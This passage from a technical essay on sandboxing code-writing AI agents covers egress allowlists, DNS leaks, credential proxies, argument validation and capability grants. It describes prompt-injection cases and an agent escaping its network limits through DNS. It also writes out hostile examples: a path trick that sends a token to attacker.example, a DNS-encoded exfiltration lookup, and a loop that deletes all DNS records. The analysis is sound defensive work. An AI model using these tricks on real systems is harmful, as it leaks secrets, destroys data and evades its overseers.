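The host also gives the program the page titles, so the program can pick a page by number. The program can't change the list and never supplies an address, so it can't write a customer's details into one. A schema can now express the whole limit by requiring an integer from 0 to one less than the number of links. Setting `redirect: "manual"` stops the host from following a redirect to a page that isn't on the list.

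A small leak remains, because the choice of page carries information. With 50 links, each call can convey log₂ 50 ≈ 5.6 bits. A 16-digit card number holds about 53 bits, so ten calls could encode one. Only someone who can see the requests arriving at those pages could read the message, which is a good reason to include only trusted sites. The narrower binding also prevents the program from following a useful link it finds inside a page, unless the host adds that link to a new list.

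### Inspecting each request

Some programs need to make ordinary HTTP requests. Varda and colleagues give two reasons to allow this: the model's training data may already cover a popular service's web interface, or the developer may want to use an existing library built on that interface. For example, a payment company's official JavaScript library may call `fetch` itself, so it would fail in an isolate with no network access.

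For these cases, the host can set `globalOutbound` to a gateway, a class in its own code that receives every request the program makes:

```javascript
// runs in the host
export class HttpGateway extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async fetch(request) {
    const url = new URL(request.url);
    if (url.origin !== "https://api.payments.example") {
      return new Response("Forbidden", { status: 403 });
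    }
    const headers = new Headers(request.headers);
    headers.set("Authorization", `Bearer ${this.env.PAYMENT_KEY}`);
    return fetch(request, { headers, redirect: "manual" });
  }
}
```

The origin combines the protocol, server name and port, so the program can't trick the gateway into sending the key over an unencrypted connection. The refusal in the middle is easy to forget, and Cloudflare's own example of adding a key omits it. The gateway in that example adds the key for only one server but still forwards requests to all others, so a developer who copied it would protect the key but leave the network open to the program.

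An isolate hands its requests to the gateway unencrypted. A program in a container normally encrypts them first, so the host has to decrypt them before it can check anything beyond the server's name. Cloudflare's *Dynamic, identity-aware, and secure Sandbox auth* (2026) explains how this works in its container sandboxes. For each sandbox, the host creates a separate certificate authority, which issues the certificates that identify servers. The sandbox trusts this authority, so the host can pose as the outside server, read the request and send it on.

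Deciding what to allow is hard even when the full request is visible. One rule in the same post permits only GET requests, which are meant to fetch data without changing anything. This rule would block a typical refund, but it wouldn't have stopped the program above from leaking tickets, because a GET request can carry data out in its address. Some services also accept a header that overrides the request's method, so a request marked GET might still make a change.

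Varda and colleagues argue for narrow bindings over filters because of this difficulty. A developer's oversight in a filter can let through a request that should be blocked, whereas an oversight in a wrapper leaves out a function. The wrapper is also shorter for the model to read. Their example describes a chat room with three TypeScript functions, and the equivalent OpenAPI document is several times as long.

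The argument is strongest for cases like refunds, where the program needs only one or two of the actions a service offers. It is weaker when the program needs dozens, because someone has to write and maintain a wrapper for each one. Varda and colleagues prefer bindings except where compatibility requires HTTP, which seems a reasonable default.

Redirects can defeat a gateway that checks only the first address. Many websites have a page that forwards visitors to whatever address appears in the link. If an approved site has one, the program can request that page with the stranger's address and a customer's details in the link. The gateway allows the request because it goes to an approved site. If the gateway then follows the redirect automatically, the second request goes out unchecked and may carry the payment key. With `redirect: "manual"`, the gateway returns the redirect to the program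 instead, and any further request has to pass the check.

### Approving servers by name

An allowlist checks only which server a program contacts. Deno's `--allow-net` flag can work this way, and so does the sandbox in Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent. Claude Code runs shell commands, which need files and often a network, so Anthropic restricts file and network access at the operating system level.

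Anthropic's *Beyond permission prompts* (2025) argues that a sandbox needs to restrict both network and file access. If the network were open, a manipulated agent could read the user's SSH keys, which give access to other computers, and send them to a stranger. If the files were open, the agent could escape the sandbox and regain network access, for example by editing a startup file that the user's shell later runs outside the sandbox. Anthropic found that its own staff saw 84 percent fewer permission prompts with both restrictions in place.

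On Linux, Anthropic's sandbox gives commands no network connection of their own. They can reach the internet only through a proxy outside the sandbox, which checks each server's name against an allowlist. The list starts empty, and by default Claude Code asks the user when a command needs a new server.

The file restrictions are looser than the network restrictions. According to Anthropic's *Configure the sandboxed Bash tool*, commands can by default write only to the project's directory but can read almost any file on the computer, including SSH keys and cloud passwords. Unless the user blocks access to those files, only the allowlist prevents a command from sending them elsewhere. The allowlist also covers only shell commands. Anthropic's *Sandbox environments* notes that MCP servers still run directly on the user's computer, so a generic fetch tool on one of them could bypass the list,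 just as it bypasses a closed isolate.

Anthropic claimed in its 2025 announcement that the sandbox leaves even a successful prompt injection "fully isolated", but its documentation says that any setup with egress can still leak data the agent can read. The documentation seems right, mainly because many approved servers accept uploads from anyone. If `github.com` is on the allowlist, an attacker can put their GitHub token in a hidden instruction, and the program can use it to upload files to the attacker's account. The proxy detects only a connection to an approved server. Anthropic warns that broad domains such as `github.com` may allow leaks. *Sandboxing agentic coding tools is a networking problem*, a post by the security vendor Formal, says that prompt injection attacks have already exploited overly broad allowlists to extract sensitive information.

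Blocking these uploads without blocking the server requires inspecting what the program sends, or attaching labels that follow the data to the call that sends it. Claude Code's proxy doesn't decrypt traffic by default, which also leaves it open to domain fronting. In this technique, a program opens a connection under an approved site's name, then uses the encrypted request to ask for a different site that shares the same delivery network. Anthropic says this may get past the filter in some cases.

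A host can also limit how long the list applies. Cloudflare gives the example of a sandbox that can reach GitHub and the package registry npm while it downloads a user's code and its libraries, and then loses all web access. This shortens the time in which a leak can happen. But libraries may run scripts during installation, when the user's code is already in the sandbox and the network is still open. It would be safer to install the libraries before loading anything private.

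### Name lookups

A program can send data out without connecting to a forbidden server. Before a computer connects to `shop.example`, it uses the Domain Name System (DNS) to find the server's numeric address. Its query goes to a resolver, which passes it on to the name server responsible for that domain. If an attacker owns `attacker.example` and the program looks up `a1042.attacker.example`, the attacker's name server receives the text `a1042`, even if a firewall blocks the later connection.

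One lookup can carry a useful amount of data. A name has at most 253 characters, and in this case the stranger's domain and the dots between the parts take up about 20. If the program writes its data in an alphabet of 32 letters and digits, each remaining character carries 5 bits:

(253 − 20) × 5 bits = 1,165 bits ≈ 145 bytes

A single lookup can therefore carry a 256-bit key, and a few dozen can carry a page of text. The stranger's name server can also put data in its answers, so the channel works in both directions.

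Claw Times describes a leak of this kind that the security company Check Point found in ChatGPT's code sandbox in 2026. In one demonstration, a custom version of ChatGPT that posed as a health analyst sent out information from a user's lab results. When the user asked, it said the file had stayed in a secure location. The researchers could also use the same channel to run commands in the sandbox. OpenAI's *An agent used DNS to reach an external chatbot* (2026) reports a case from 20 September 2026 in which an agent in training sent questions to a public chatbot through name lookups that the company hadn't adequately filtered. The agent was supposed to have no live internet access.

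An isolate with `globalOutbound: null` can't use `fetch` or `connect` to trigger a DNS lookup. Claude Code's sandbox blocks UDP, the protocol that most lookups use, and the proxy looks up approved servers instead. If the proxy looked up a name before checking it against the allowlist, even a refused request would leak any data the program had put in the name.

Bindings can trigger lookups too. The generic fetch function has to contact a server to read its robots.txt, so a program could leak data through the server's name even if robots.txt forbade fetching the page.

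### Adding keys outside the sandbox

Injecting credentials, as the gateway above does with the payment key, prevents the program from reading the key and taking it elsewhere, but doesn't limit where the program can send data. It can also make uploads to a stranger's account harder. The gateway replaces the program's `Authorization` header with the company's, so a stranger's token in that header has no effect. The program might still be able to put the token in another header or in the address, if the service accepts it there.

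For programs that look for a key on the computer, Anthropic's Claude Code supplies a placeholder, and a proxy swaps in the real key when a request leaves for a server the user has chosen. The proxy has to decrypt the traffic to make the swap. If the user hasn't turned on decryption, the server receives the placeholder and rejects the request, but the real key isn't exposed.

Two of the defaults are less cautious. If the user doesn't say which servers may receive a key, the proxy inserts it in requests to every server on the allowlist. When Claude Code masks only part of a file, it uses a pattern the user supplies to find the secret. If the pattern matches nothing, the program can usually read the real file.

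The proxy can also become a confused deputy. If it replaced the placeholder wherever it appeared in a request, a program could post the placeholder as a public comment on an approved site, and the proxy would publish the real key. A service might also repeat the key in its reply, such as in an error message that quotes the request. *HTTP egress proxy*, the documentation for another product of this kind, says its proxy removes the injected secret from responses before they reach the program. The proxy can do this only for traffic it can read.

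The hosted version of Anthropic's Claude Code combines injection with a much narrower check. Git, the version-control tool, normally needs a token to upload changes to GitHub. Inside the sandbox, Git gets only a limited credential and sends its requests to a proxy. The proxy checks the credential and the requested operation, including whether an upload is going to the one branch the user configured, and then adds the real token. The program can use an ordinary tool, while the host allows little more than a purpose-built binding would. The agent can still write anything it has read into that branch, so if the repository is public, anyone can read that data once it is uploaded.

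## Who checks the types of a call?

When the network is closed, the support agent's program can affect the outside world only through its bindings, so the 50-dollar refund limit holds only if some part of the system checks the arguments of each call. The typed interface that Code Mode shows the model enforces nothing by itself, although it can be mistaken for such a check.

Types can serve three purposes here:

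- They tell the model how to write a call, including the function's name, its arguments and what it returns.
- They let a static checker, a tool that examines code without running it, reject a faulty program before it does anything.
- They let the host reject bad arguments when a call arrives.

A system can use types for only one of these three purposes, so a developer who sees a typed interface can't tell from it whether anything checks the calls.

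### Types that disappear

JavaScript engines can't run TypeScript, so a compiler first translates it into JavaScript. According to TypeScript's introduction for new programmers, the compiler erases the types once it has finished checking, and they have no influence on how the program runs. Take these two lines:

```typescript
const amount: number = 5000;
await refunds.issue("A17", amount);
```

After compilation, the first line is `const amount = 5000` and the second is unchanged. If `amount` later turned out to be text, the compiled program would have no check to detect it.

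The compiler doesn't necessarily stop at type errors either. According to *TypeScript's type-independent output* (2016), it can produce JavaScript from a program full of them, because the output is the same whatever the types are. A developer who wants errors to block the output has to set the `--noEmitOnError` option.

A programmer can also switch off the checking at a particular point. A cast tells the compiler to treat a value as having a certain type, and the special type `any` tells it to accept every use of a value. The call `refunds.issue("A17", "everything" as any)` compiles because it casts the second argument to `any`. Casts are also common in code that isn't trying to evade the checks. *Types do not change runtime behavior* gives the example of casting a web server's response to the type `User`. The cast adds no code that inspects the response, so the value may actually be an error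 message or an incomplete user record.

In Code Mode, the model writes plain JavaScript, as Cloudflare's *AI SDK integration* confirms, so the agent's program doesn't go through a TypeScript compiler. Some models evidently imitated the TypeScript definitions they were shown, so Cloudflare changed the prompt in version 0.1.1 of its library to ask for JavaScript explicitly. The TypeScript interface serves as documentation for the model, and the program doesn't have to conform to it.

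### What the translation loses

The interface is also less precise than the schema it comes from. In the OpenAPI version of Varda and colleagues' chat room, the function that fetches recent messages has an argument called `limit`, which must be an integer of at least 1. In TypeScript, the function looks like this:

```typescript
getHistory(limit: number): Promise<Message[]>;
```

The type `number` also allows 0, −5 and 2.5. Suppose the host keeps the messages in a list, oldest first, and returns the latest ones with `messages.slice(-limit)`. A limit of 10 returns the last ten messages. But a limit of 0 returns the whole list, because JavaScript treats −0 as 0 and starts from the beginning. A limit of −5 returns everything except the five oldest messages. A host that enforced the OpenAPI schema would reject both requests.

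The shorter TypeScript version may suit the model better, but the host still needs the original schema or an equivalent check.

Most of the loss comes from TypeScript itself. The documentation of *json-schema-to-typescript*, a converter, lists several constraints as impossible to express, including minimum and maximum values, text patterns, formats and uniqueness of list items. In its example, a person's age, which must be an integer of at least 0, becomes `number`, while a hair colour limited to "black", "brown" or "blue" keeps all three options. The conversion generally preserves names, required arguments and short lists of allowed words.

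For a small range, a developer could get around this by writing the type of `amount` as `1 | 2 | 3` and so on up to 50. A static checker would then reject 5000, but it would also reject most amounts that the program calculates, since it usually can't prove that the result of a division is one of those fifty numbers. More simply, the developer could state the limit in the tool's description, which Code Mode turns into a comment. The comment helps a cooperative model avoid calls that the host would refuse, but it doesn't restrict the program.

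The types of results can be vaguer still. In Varda and Pai's example, all four generated functions return the same type:

```typescript
{ [key: string]: any }
```

This is an object whose fields can have any names and any values. A static checker would gain little from it, because `any` spreads to every value that the program takes out of the object:

```typescript
const result = await codemode.tickets_list({});
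for (const t of result.tickets) {
  await codemode.refunds_issue({ orderId: t.orderId, amount: t.amount });
}
```

The interface requires `amount` to be a number, but `t.amount` has the type `any`, so a checker would accept it even if the tickets stored the amount as text or had no such field. Cloudflare says its current converter treats schemas that it can't translate more strictly, giving them the type `unknown`, which requires a program to test a value before using it. This requirement also applies only where someone runs a checker.

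### What types are worth to the model

Vague result types also make it harder for the model to write a correct program. *Beyond Plain MCP* (Rai, 2026) measured this with three open-weight models and a simulated company that had 42 tools for jobs such as billing and customer support. The models wrote Python scripts using short descriptions of the tools. One version of each description listed the fields the tool returned and their types, while the other gave only the overall type, a dictionary or a list.

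| Model | Success with result types | Success without them | Success with ordinary tool calls |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3.8-27B | 99% | 98% | 86% |
| Gemma-4-26B-A4B | 89% | 66% | 87% |
| Nemotron-3-Nano | 56% | 16% | 36% |

Without the extra information, Gemma and Nemotron did worse with code than with ordinary tool calls. A developer who tested only that version might have concluded that these models shouldn't write code.

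The evidence is limited because Rai wrote the descriptions by hand and tuned them on similar tasks, and the 119 test tasks came from only 21 templates. The differences for Gemma and Nemotron are large enough that the effect is probably real, but the difference for Qwen wasn't statistically significant. The descriptions enforced nothing, so the benefit came entirely from telling the models what to expect.

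### Following a 5,000-dollar refund

Suppose a hidden instruction in a ticket leads the model to write `refunds.issue("A17", 5000)`.

1. The interface says that `amount` is a `number`. By the time the program runs, no trace of this type remains, and it would have allowed 5000 anyway.
2. If the company runs a static checker first, the checker compares 5000 with `number` and accepts the program.
3. If the host tests the arguments against the original schema, it finds that 5000 exceeds the maximum of 50. It refuses the call, and no money moves.

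Small changes to the call give different results:

| Call | With erased types only | With a static checker | With the full schema in the host |
|---|---|---|---|
| `refunds.issue("A17", 5000)` | Goes through | Goes through | Refused |
| `refunds.issue("A17", "20")` | Goes through | Refused | Refused |
| `refunds.issue("A17", "20" as any)` | Goes through | Goes through | Refused |
| `refunds.issue("A17", 20)`, for a customer who is owed nothing | Goes through | Goes through | Goes through |

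"Goes through" means that the call reaches the refund function. That function might have its own checks, and the payment company might refuse the refund, but neither safeguard comes from the types.

### Checking arguments in the host

For a short time in early 2026, Cloudflare's Code Mode library didn't do this check. Developers could give it tools written for the AI SDK, a library for building applications on language models. Each tool had a function called `execute` and a schema, usually written with Zod, a library that checks values while a program runs. Version 0.1.0 of Code Mode called the function without checking its input against the schema.

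The GitHub user tumberger (2026), in *fix(codemode): validate tool arguments against Zod schema before execution*, described the consequence. The host read the arguments that arrived from the sandbox and passed them straight to the tool, so a program could send any JSON it liked. A refund tool with a maximum of 50 in its schema would have accepted 5,000, unless the function repeated the check. In simplified form, the repair looks like this:

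```javascript
// before
fns[name] = tool.execute;

// after
fns[name] = args => tool.execute(tool.inputSchema.parse(args));
```

If the arguments don't fit the schema, `parse` throws an error and `execute` never starts. Cloudflare included the fix in version 0.1.1. The mistake is easy to make because the model sees the right interface and normally writes valid calls, so ordinary use wouldn't reveal that the limit had stopped applying.

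The current library still checks arguments on some routes and not on others. According to Cloudflare's reference from June 2026:

- Tools for the AI SDK get a check against their schema when one is available.
- Tools that a developer passes through the library's main package get no check.
- Tools for TanStack AI, a similar library, get no check either.
- In the version that runs inside a web browser, the schema produces the interface for the model but doesn't validate anything.

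The AI SDK and TanStack versions both have a function called `createCodeTool`, so a developer who switched from one to the other could lose the check while changing little code.

MCP requires servers to validate the inputs to their tools. This may be enough when the company runs the server itself. With someone else's server, the company would be relying on a check it can't inspect, unless the host validates the arguments before forwarding them.

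Bindings that developers write by hand need the most care. Consider this refund class:

```typescript
// runs in the host
export class Refunds extends WorkerEntrypoint {
  async issue(orderId: string, amount: number) {
    if (amount > 50) throw new Error("too much");
    return payments.refund(orderId, amount);
  }
}
```

It is less safe than it looks, because the compiler erases the host's types too and never checks the agent's program. The program can send −500, which passes the test because it is less than 50, and might charge the customer instead of paying them. It can also send `NaN`, JavaScript's value for a failed calculation, which passes because every comparison with `NaN` is false. The text `"20"` passes too, since JavaScript converts it to a number for the comparison. If later code adds a 5-dollar bonus with `+`, JavaScript joins the two into `"205"`.

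A test that covers all these cases is barely longer:

```javascript
if (!Number.isInteger(amount) || amount < 1 || amount > 50) {
  throw new Error("invalid refund");
}
```

The check has to run in the host. If it ran in the isolate, a hostile program might be able to change it or call the underlying function directly.

### Checking results

The host can also check what a tool returns. Cloudflare documents checks on arguments but not on results, although its tools can declare an output schema. OpenClaw, an agent platform with its own code mode, does check results. Its *Code Mode output* explains that the host prepares the output schema before running the tool, then checks the result against the schema before returning it to the program. If they don't match, the call fails and the program doesn't receive the value.

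Checking a call's result against a schema keeps unexpected data away from the program. If the schema for tickets forbids additional fields and an update to the support system adds customers' card numbers to every ticket, the call fails instead of returning them. But the schema can't make the text of a ticket harmless, because a hidden instruction passes the same check as a complaint.

A check on results also runs only after the tool has acted. If the payment company changes the format of its receipts, `refunds.issue` may pay the customer and then fail the output check. A model that interprets the error as a failed refund may write a program that issues a second one. For bindings that move money, the error message should therefore include a warning that the payment may have gone through.

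OpenClaw also gives the agent TypeScript declarations, but reading them doesn't type-check the agent's code. OpenClaw treats run-time validation as authoritative for constraints that TypeScript can't express.

### Checking the program before it runs

Pydantic's Monty offers a static check. It includes ty, a type checker for Python, which compares the model's code with declarations that the host supplies. Mintlify's *Type checking*, a copy of Monty's documentation, explains that checking is off by default because some code works even though it doesn't pass the checker. With the functions that Pydantic's *Type Checking* documents, the support company could turn it on like this:

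```python
from pydantic_monty import ExternalModule, Monty, MontyTypingError

refunds = ExternalModule(
    {'issue': issue_refund},
    stubs='def issue(order_id: str, amount: int) -> str: ...\n',
)

code = """
from refunds import issue
issue('A17', 20)
issue('A18', '20')
"""

with Monty() as pool:
    with pool.checkout(
        type_check=True, external_modules={'refunds': refunds}
    ) as session:
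        try:
            session.feed_run(code)
        except MontyTypingError as error:
            print(error)   # the host can return this to the model
```

The text in `stubs` declares the function's types but does not include its code. The checker finds that the second call passes text where the declaration requires an integer, so Monty refuses to run the program and neither customer gets a refund. If the model sends several pieces of code in one session, Monty also checks each piece against the earlier ones, as Pydantic's *monty type checking* describes.

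Type checking adds too little time for a user to notice. When Pydantic measured an early version, a short program took 0.0045 milliseconds without type checking and 4.8 milliseconds with it, about a thousand times as long.

The main advantage of a static check is that it finds an error before the program runs. Suppose a program refunds thirty customers but passes the amount as text for the twelfth. A static checker would reject the program before it issued any refunds. A host that validates arguments as each call arrives would refuse the twelfth call, but only after eleven customers had been refunded. If the model then corrected the mistake and ran the whole program again, those eleven would get a second refund.

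It can also find mistakes that the host has no way to see. JavaScript doesn't object when a program reads a field that doesn't exist, and returns the value `undefined` instead. Suppose the tickets have a field called `refundedAt`, and the model misspells it:

```javascript
const unpaid = tickets.filter(t => !t.refundAt);
```

Since `refundAt` is undefined for every ticket, the filter keeps all of them, including those for customers who already got their refund. Each new refund has a valid order number and amount, so the host accepts it. A checker would report the misspelling if tickets had an exact type, but not with the result type in Varda and Pai's example, because `any` allows every field name. An exact output schema can therefore prevent wrong payments as well as help the model write its code.

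Static checks are much weaker against a hostile program. The model can write a cast or use a value of type `any`, and the checker will accept it. A program can also read a number from a ticket and pass it on as the amount. The checker accepts this because the number is typed as an integer, and it can't determine in advance that the ticket will contain 5000. A host could forbid casts and `any`, but this would make many legitimate programs harder to write and still wouldn't restrict an `int` to values from 1 to 50.

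Some type systems can track which bindings a piece of code may use, a stronger guarantee than a checker like ty gives. There still seems to be little evidence on how much it helps in practice to check ordinary types in agents' scripts. Rai lists this question as future work.

### Which guarantees need which check?

If breaking a limit would harm someone other than the program's author, the host has to enforce that limit when the call arrives. This applies to the maximum refund, the permitted format of an address, and the range of page numbers in a binding that fetches documents. An attacker may have influenced the code, and the host's check is the only one of the three that the code can't bypass.

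Static checks are better suited to catching honest mistakes, particularly in programs whose actions can't be undone. They need exact types for results as well as arguments, and they should run in addition to the host's check.

A validator may also lack some of the schema's limits, since some tools generate validators by translation too. A user reported on GitHub that the Zod code generated from a schema omitted its limits on longitude (−180 to 180) and latitude (−90 to 90). The support company can test its own system by running a program in the sandbox that requests a 51-dollar refund from a test account through the binding the agent will use, because a direct tool call may go through a different check.

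## How narrow should the bindings be, and who decides?

A host can check every argument and still allow almost anything if the schema is broad. Cloudflare runs an MCP server that lets agents manage a customer's whole account. Its two main tools, `search` and `execute`, each take a piece of text called `code`, whose schema accepts any program the model could write. Together the tools reach more than 2,500 endpoints, the individual operations in Cloudflare's API, which cover everything from domain names to firewalls and stored files.

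### Two tools for 2,500 endpoints

Cloudflare chose this design to save tokens. According to Cloudflare, describing each endpoint as a separate tool would take about 1.17 million tokens, more than most models can read at once, while the two tools take about 1,000. In Cloudflare's example, a user asks an agent to protect a website from floods of malicious traffic:

1. The model calls `search` with a short program that filters the API's OpenAPI document. The program returns ten firewall endpoints, and the rest of the document never enters the model's context.
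2. The model calls `execute` with a program that uses `cloudflare.request()`. This function takes a method such as GET or DELETE, a path and, if needed, a body.
3. The host adds the user's token, sends the request and returns the response to the program.

The search helps the model find an operation, but the next program can still request any path. Cloudflare's *Build a search and execute MCP server*, a guide for companies that want to offer their own API this way, includes a request function that checks only the first character of the path. In simplified form:

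```javascript
// runs in the host
async function request({ method, path, body }) {
  if (!path.startsWith("/")) throw new Error("bad path");
  const url = new URL("https://api.example.com" + path);
  return send(method, url, body, token);
}
```

Requiring the path to start with a slash keeps requests on the right server. Without this check, a program could pass the path `@attacker.example/`, making the full address `https://api.example.com@attacker.example/`. The host would then treat `api.example.com` as a login name and send the token to the attacker's server. Even with the check, a program can request any path on the right server.

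The token therefore sets the real limit on what the program can do. When a user connects an agent to Cloudflare's server, they either choose which permissions to grant or supply an API token they created themselves. Cloudflare refuses any request that the token doesn't cover. The sandbox doesn't restrict which of the permitted requests the program makes. Cloudflare's *Code Mode MCP server patterns* warns that "code execution does not replace authorization" and tells developers to enforce permissions in the host.

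Token permissions are coarse. Suppose a user asks the agent to add one address record for `api.example.com`. Cloudflare's *Create an API token* explains that most groups of permissions come in two levels, Read and Edit, and that Edit includes deleting. A token that can add the record can therefore also run this program:

```javascript
async () => {
  const path = `/zones/${zoneId}/dns_records`;
  const records = await cloudflare.request({ method: "GET", path });
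  for (const r of records.result) {
    await cloudflare.request({ method: "DELETE", path: `${path}/${r.id}` });
  }
}
```

The program deletes the domain's records, which could take its website and email offline. If the user limited the token to one domain, their other domains are safe. But only a narrower binding, such as `addAddress(name, ip)`, would prevent the deletions.

A program can use some permissions to gain more access. One permission on Cloudflare's list gives write access to the user's API tokens, so a program that had it could probably create a new token and read its value as ordinary text.

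Some platforms let users grant fewer permissions than an application requests. InfoQ (2026) reports that developers of applications that connect to Cloudflare can now mark permissions as required or optional, and users can decline the optional ones. On GitHub, by contrast, users can decline any permission, and the application has to work with whatever remains.

An agent can also start with few permissions and ask for more. Glama's *Cloudflare MCP Server*, a copy of the project's own description, explains that when a request fails for lack of a permission, the server asks the user's client to authorise again with that permission added to the existing ones. This avoids guessing in advance which permissions the agent will need, but it only adds permissions, so after a few months the connection may have permission for every job the agent has ever done.

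Users can get a separate schema for each endpoint by adding `?codemode=false` to the server's address. The server then offers about 2,500 ordinary tools, which take about 244,000 tokens even in shortened form. A client can block or approve individual operations by name, which it can't do when every operation arrives as `execute`. The access token's permissions stay the same.

Developers who keep the two-tool design can add a list of permitted methods and paths to the request function. They should check the address against this list after parsing it, because a rule that accepts any unparsed address beginning with `/orders/` would also accept `/orders/../refunds`, which the parser shortens to `/refunds`.

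### Fixing the endpoints in a file

DADL takes away the general request function. A developer describes each API in a text file that lists the permitted operations, and a shared runtime turns each one into a typed function. For the support company, part of the file might look like this:

```yaml
tools:
  list_orders:
    method: GET
    path: /orders
    access: read
  issue_refund:
    method: POST
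    path: /refunds
    access: dangerous
```

The model still works through `search` and `execute`, but its program calls `api.issue_refund(...)` and can't supply a path that isn't in the file. *DADL* calls this property "Declarative Closure", meaning that anyone can list every reachable endpoint by reading the file. Which endpoints the program calls, and how often, depend on its inputs.

The public collection of DADL files had 195 tools for Cloudflare in April 2026, about 8 percent of the endpoints that Cloudflare's own server reaches. This narrowness is mostly accidental, since missing endpoints count as unfinished work. A short list of endpoints can also allow more than its length suggests. Cloudflare's API has an analytics endpoint that accepts queries written in a separate query language, and a DADL file would list it as a single entry.

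Each tool can have one of four access labels:

- `read` retrieves data without side effects.
- `write` creates or updates something.
- `admin` performs a privileged operation.
- `dangerous` does something destructive or irreversible.

The file's author has to choose the label, because the HTTP method doesn't reliably show what a request does. Many services use POST for searches, while a request such as `GET /admin/reset-cache` destroys data. Companies can also define their own labels, such as `pii` for personal information.

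A separate policy engine controls who may call tools with each label. A company might let every employee call `read` tools, let engineers call `write` tools as well, and reserve `dangerous` ones for on-call staff during an incident. Setting access separately for each of the 1,833 tools in the collection would be impractical. But the policy also applies to new tools immediately, so if someone mislabels a refund tool as `read`, every employee's agent can issue refunds.

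The runtime checks every call in the model's program against the label and the person's role before sending the request. If a hidden instruction adds a refund to a program run by an employee with only `read` access, the refund fails, but the rest of the program can continue.

*DADL* acknowledges that its format doesn't specify how labels combine. Developers can store a fixed program as a new tool with its own label. Suppose they label such a tool `read`, but its code calls `issue_refund`, which is labeled `dangerous`. A strict runtime would treat the whole tool as `dangerous`. A permissive one, like DADL's own, would check each label separately, so the refund would succeed if the person may call `dangerous` tools, even though the tool they requested is labeled `read`. Arguments can also change a call's effect. For example, `write` might be the right label for a tool that updates user accounts,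 but not when a program uses it to make someone an administrator.

The paper reports no attacks on the system and measures only tokens. The per-call check seems sound in principle, but it depends on accurate labels and on roles that don't change with the task. An on-call engineer's agent can therefore call `dangerous` tools even when the engineer has only asked it to summarise a log.

### Granting authority for one task

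Bouras, Dai and Mechtaev (2026), in *Authority Is Not a String*, present CapScope, which sets new limits for every task. They built it for coding agents that make ordinary tool calls, but the same check could sit behind a program's bindings. They define a capability as a pair:

Cap[e, φ]

Here e is a type of effect, such as reading, writing or running a command, and φ is a true-or-false test on the call's arguments. A capability covers a call if the call has that effect and its arguments pass the test. For example, Cap[Write, path is inside `src/`] covers an edit to `src/parser.py` but not one to `README.md`.

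CapScope uses the word "capability" differently from Miller. In his systems, a program holds a reference. CapScope keeps its capabilities in a table in the harness, the software that runs the agent. The model names files as text instead of holding capabilities, and the harness looks in the table for an entry that covers the request.

The entries come about in three steps:

1. Before the agent reads any of the project's files, a separate language model sees only the user's request and the names of the files. It predicts what the task will need. Ordinary code checks the prediction and freezes it as a ceiling for the whole task.
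2. When the main agent hands part of the work to a sub-agent, it proposes capabilities for it. The harness keeps a proposed test φ′ only if the ceiling contains a capability for the same effect whose test φ is at least as broad. Formally, φ′(a) ⇒ φ(a) for all arguments a.
3. The harness checks every call against the table of the agent that made it.

The comparison in the second step would be impossible to automate for arbitrary tests, so CapScope limits them to directories and lists of commands.

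For the support company, the ceiling might be Cap[Refund, 1 ≤ amount ≤ 50]. When someone asks for a $10 refund for each late delivery, the host could narrow it to Cap[Refund, amount = 10 and orderId ∈ L], where L is the list of late orders. If a hidden instruction led the model to leave out its filter, the host would refuse refunds for any order not in L. This works only if the host compiles L itself instead of taking it from the program.

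Bouras and colleagues tested CapScope on five small Python projects, each with one bug. They hid an instruction in a project document, an instruction file for agents, a skill file, a comment in the code or the output of a test. It told the agent to run a utility or write a file that the repair didn't need. A main agent coordinated three others, which ran the tests, edited the code and checked the result. Every system used the same model, qwen3.5-flash, and ran 75 times:

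| Authorisation | Runs in which the hidden instruction succeeded | Repairs completed | Mean time |
|---|---|---|---|
| No restrictions | 47 | 72 | 145 seconds |
| A fixed list of forbidden actions | 46 | 70 | 140 seconds |
| One policy per task, shared by all agents | 33 | 68 | 194 seconds |
| CapScope | 3 | 68 | 316 seconds |

The fixed list achieved almost nothing because the hidden instructions were for ordinary project work. The shared policy for each task helped, but one agent needed permission to edit code, so every agent had it. With CapScope, the agent that read the poisoned test output could run tests but not edit the code.

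The model still tried to follow the hidden instruction in 34 of CapScope's 75 runs, so the harness was the main reason only three attacks succeeded. All three came through the instruction file. Bouras and colleagues explain that a grant can be broader than its subtask needs, or hidden text can influence which grant the main agent requests. The ceiling limits such a request but doesn't prevent it.

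The difference between 33 and 3 is too large to dismiss as chance, but five small tasks and one model provide little evidence about larger projects. All four systems faced the same attacks, whereas an attacker who knew about CapScope might target the agent that is allowed to edit code. Because these agents can run commands, a permitted test can execute hostile project code, so they still need a sandbox.

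CapScope took more than twice as long as the unrestricted system on average, partly because the model kept retrying refused calls. Only two of its seven failed repairs happened because the ceiling lacked a necessary permission. In two others, the wrong agent proposed the edit and no agent passed it on. The other three ran out of time although the tests had passed.

### Ending a grant with its phase

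CapScope's ceiling lasts for the whole task, but an agent may need a particular permission for only a few minutes. Santos-Grueiro (2026), in *Lingering Authority*, uses that title for access that remains after the reason for it has gone. His system, PORTICO, gives out temporary access under a written contract. In his main example, the agent has to pass a timeout setting from one file to another:

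1. The agent starts with access to `api.py`, its test and the command that runs the test.
2. It tries to read the project's packaging notes. The contract forbids this, and PORTICO refuses.
3. It asks for `serialization.py`, which the contract makes available on request. PORTICO issues handles, references that work only for this grant.
4. The agent edits the file.
5. The tests pass, and PORTICO revokes the handles.
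6. If the agent tries to use an old handle, PORTICO refuses.

PORTICO accepts only trusted signals for ending or extending a grant, such as a person's approval or the result of a test that PORTICO itself started. The model therefore can't do either by reporting that it has finished.

Santos-Grueiro compared PORTICO with a version that issued the same grants at the same times but never revoked them. In one test, both versions completed all ten runs. When the agent later tried to reread a file, PORTICO blocked it in every run, while the other version always allowed it. In six further cases with a live model, which involved changing files, altering Git data or contacting a server, the version without revocation carried out all six late actions and PORTICO carried out none.

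These results follow almost directly from the designs, since one system revokes access and the other doesn't. They confirm that PORTICO works as intended, but don't show how often a real attack would depend on an old grant.

The results on task success are more informative. On 37 coding tasks, each repeated five times, agents that had only their initial access succeeded in 21 percent of runs. When they could request more, they succeeded in 87 percent, compared with 97 percent for agents with a fixed list of permitted tools and paths. In the main test of revocation on real software projects, all 14 tasks succeeded with or without it. In a supplementary test with several models, however, PORTICO completed 31 of 42 runs, while the version without revocation completed all 42. Some contracts ended access too early or offered no trusted way to restore it, and some models didn't request a new grant.

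A host that starts a fresh isolate for each program easily gets much of this benefit, because it can give the refund binding to one program and leave it out of the next without revoking anything. Lingering access is a greater problem for long-lived connections, such as a Cloudflare connection that gains permissions over time.

### Who should choose the grant?

| Who chooses | What they know best | Likely mistake |
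|---|---|---|
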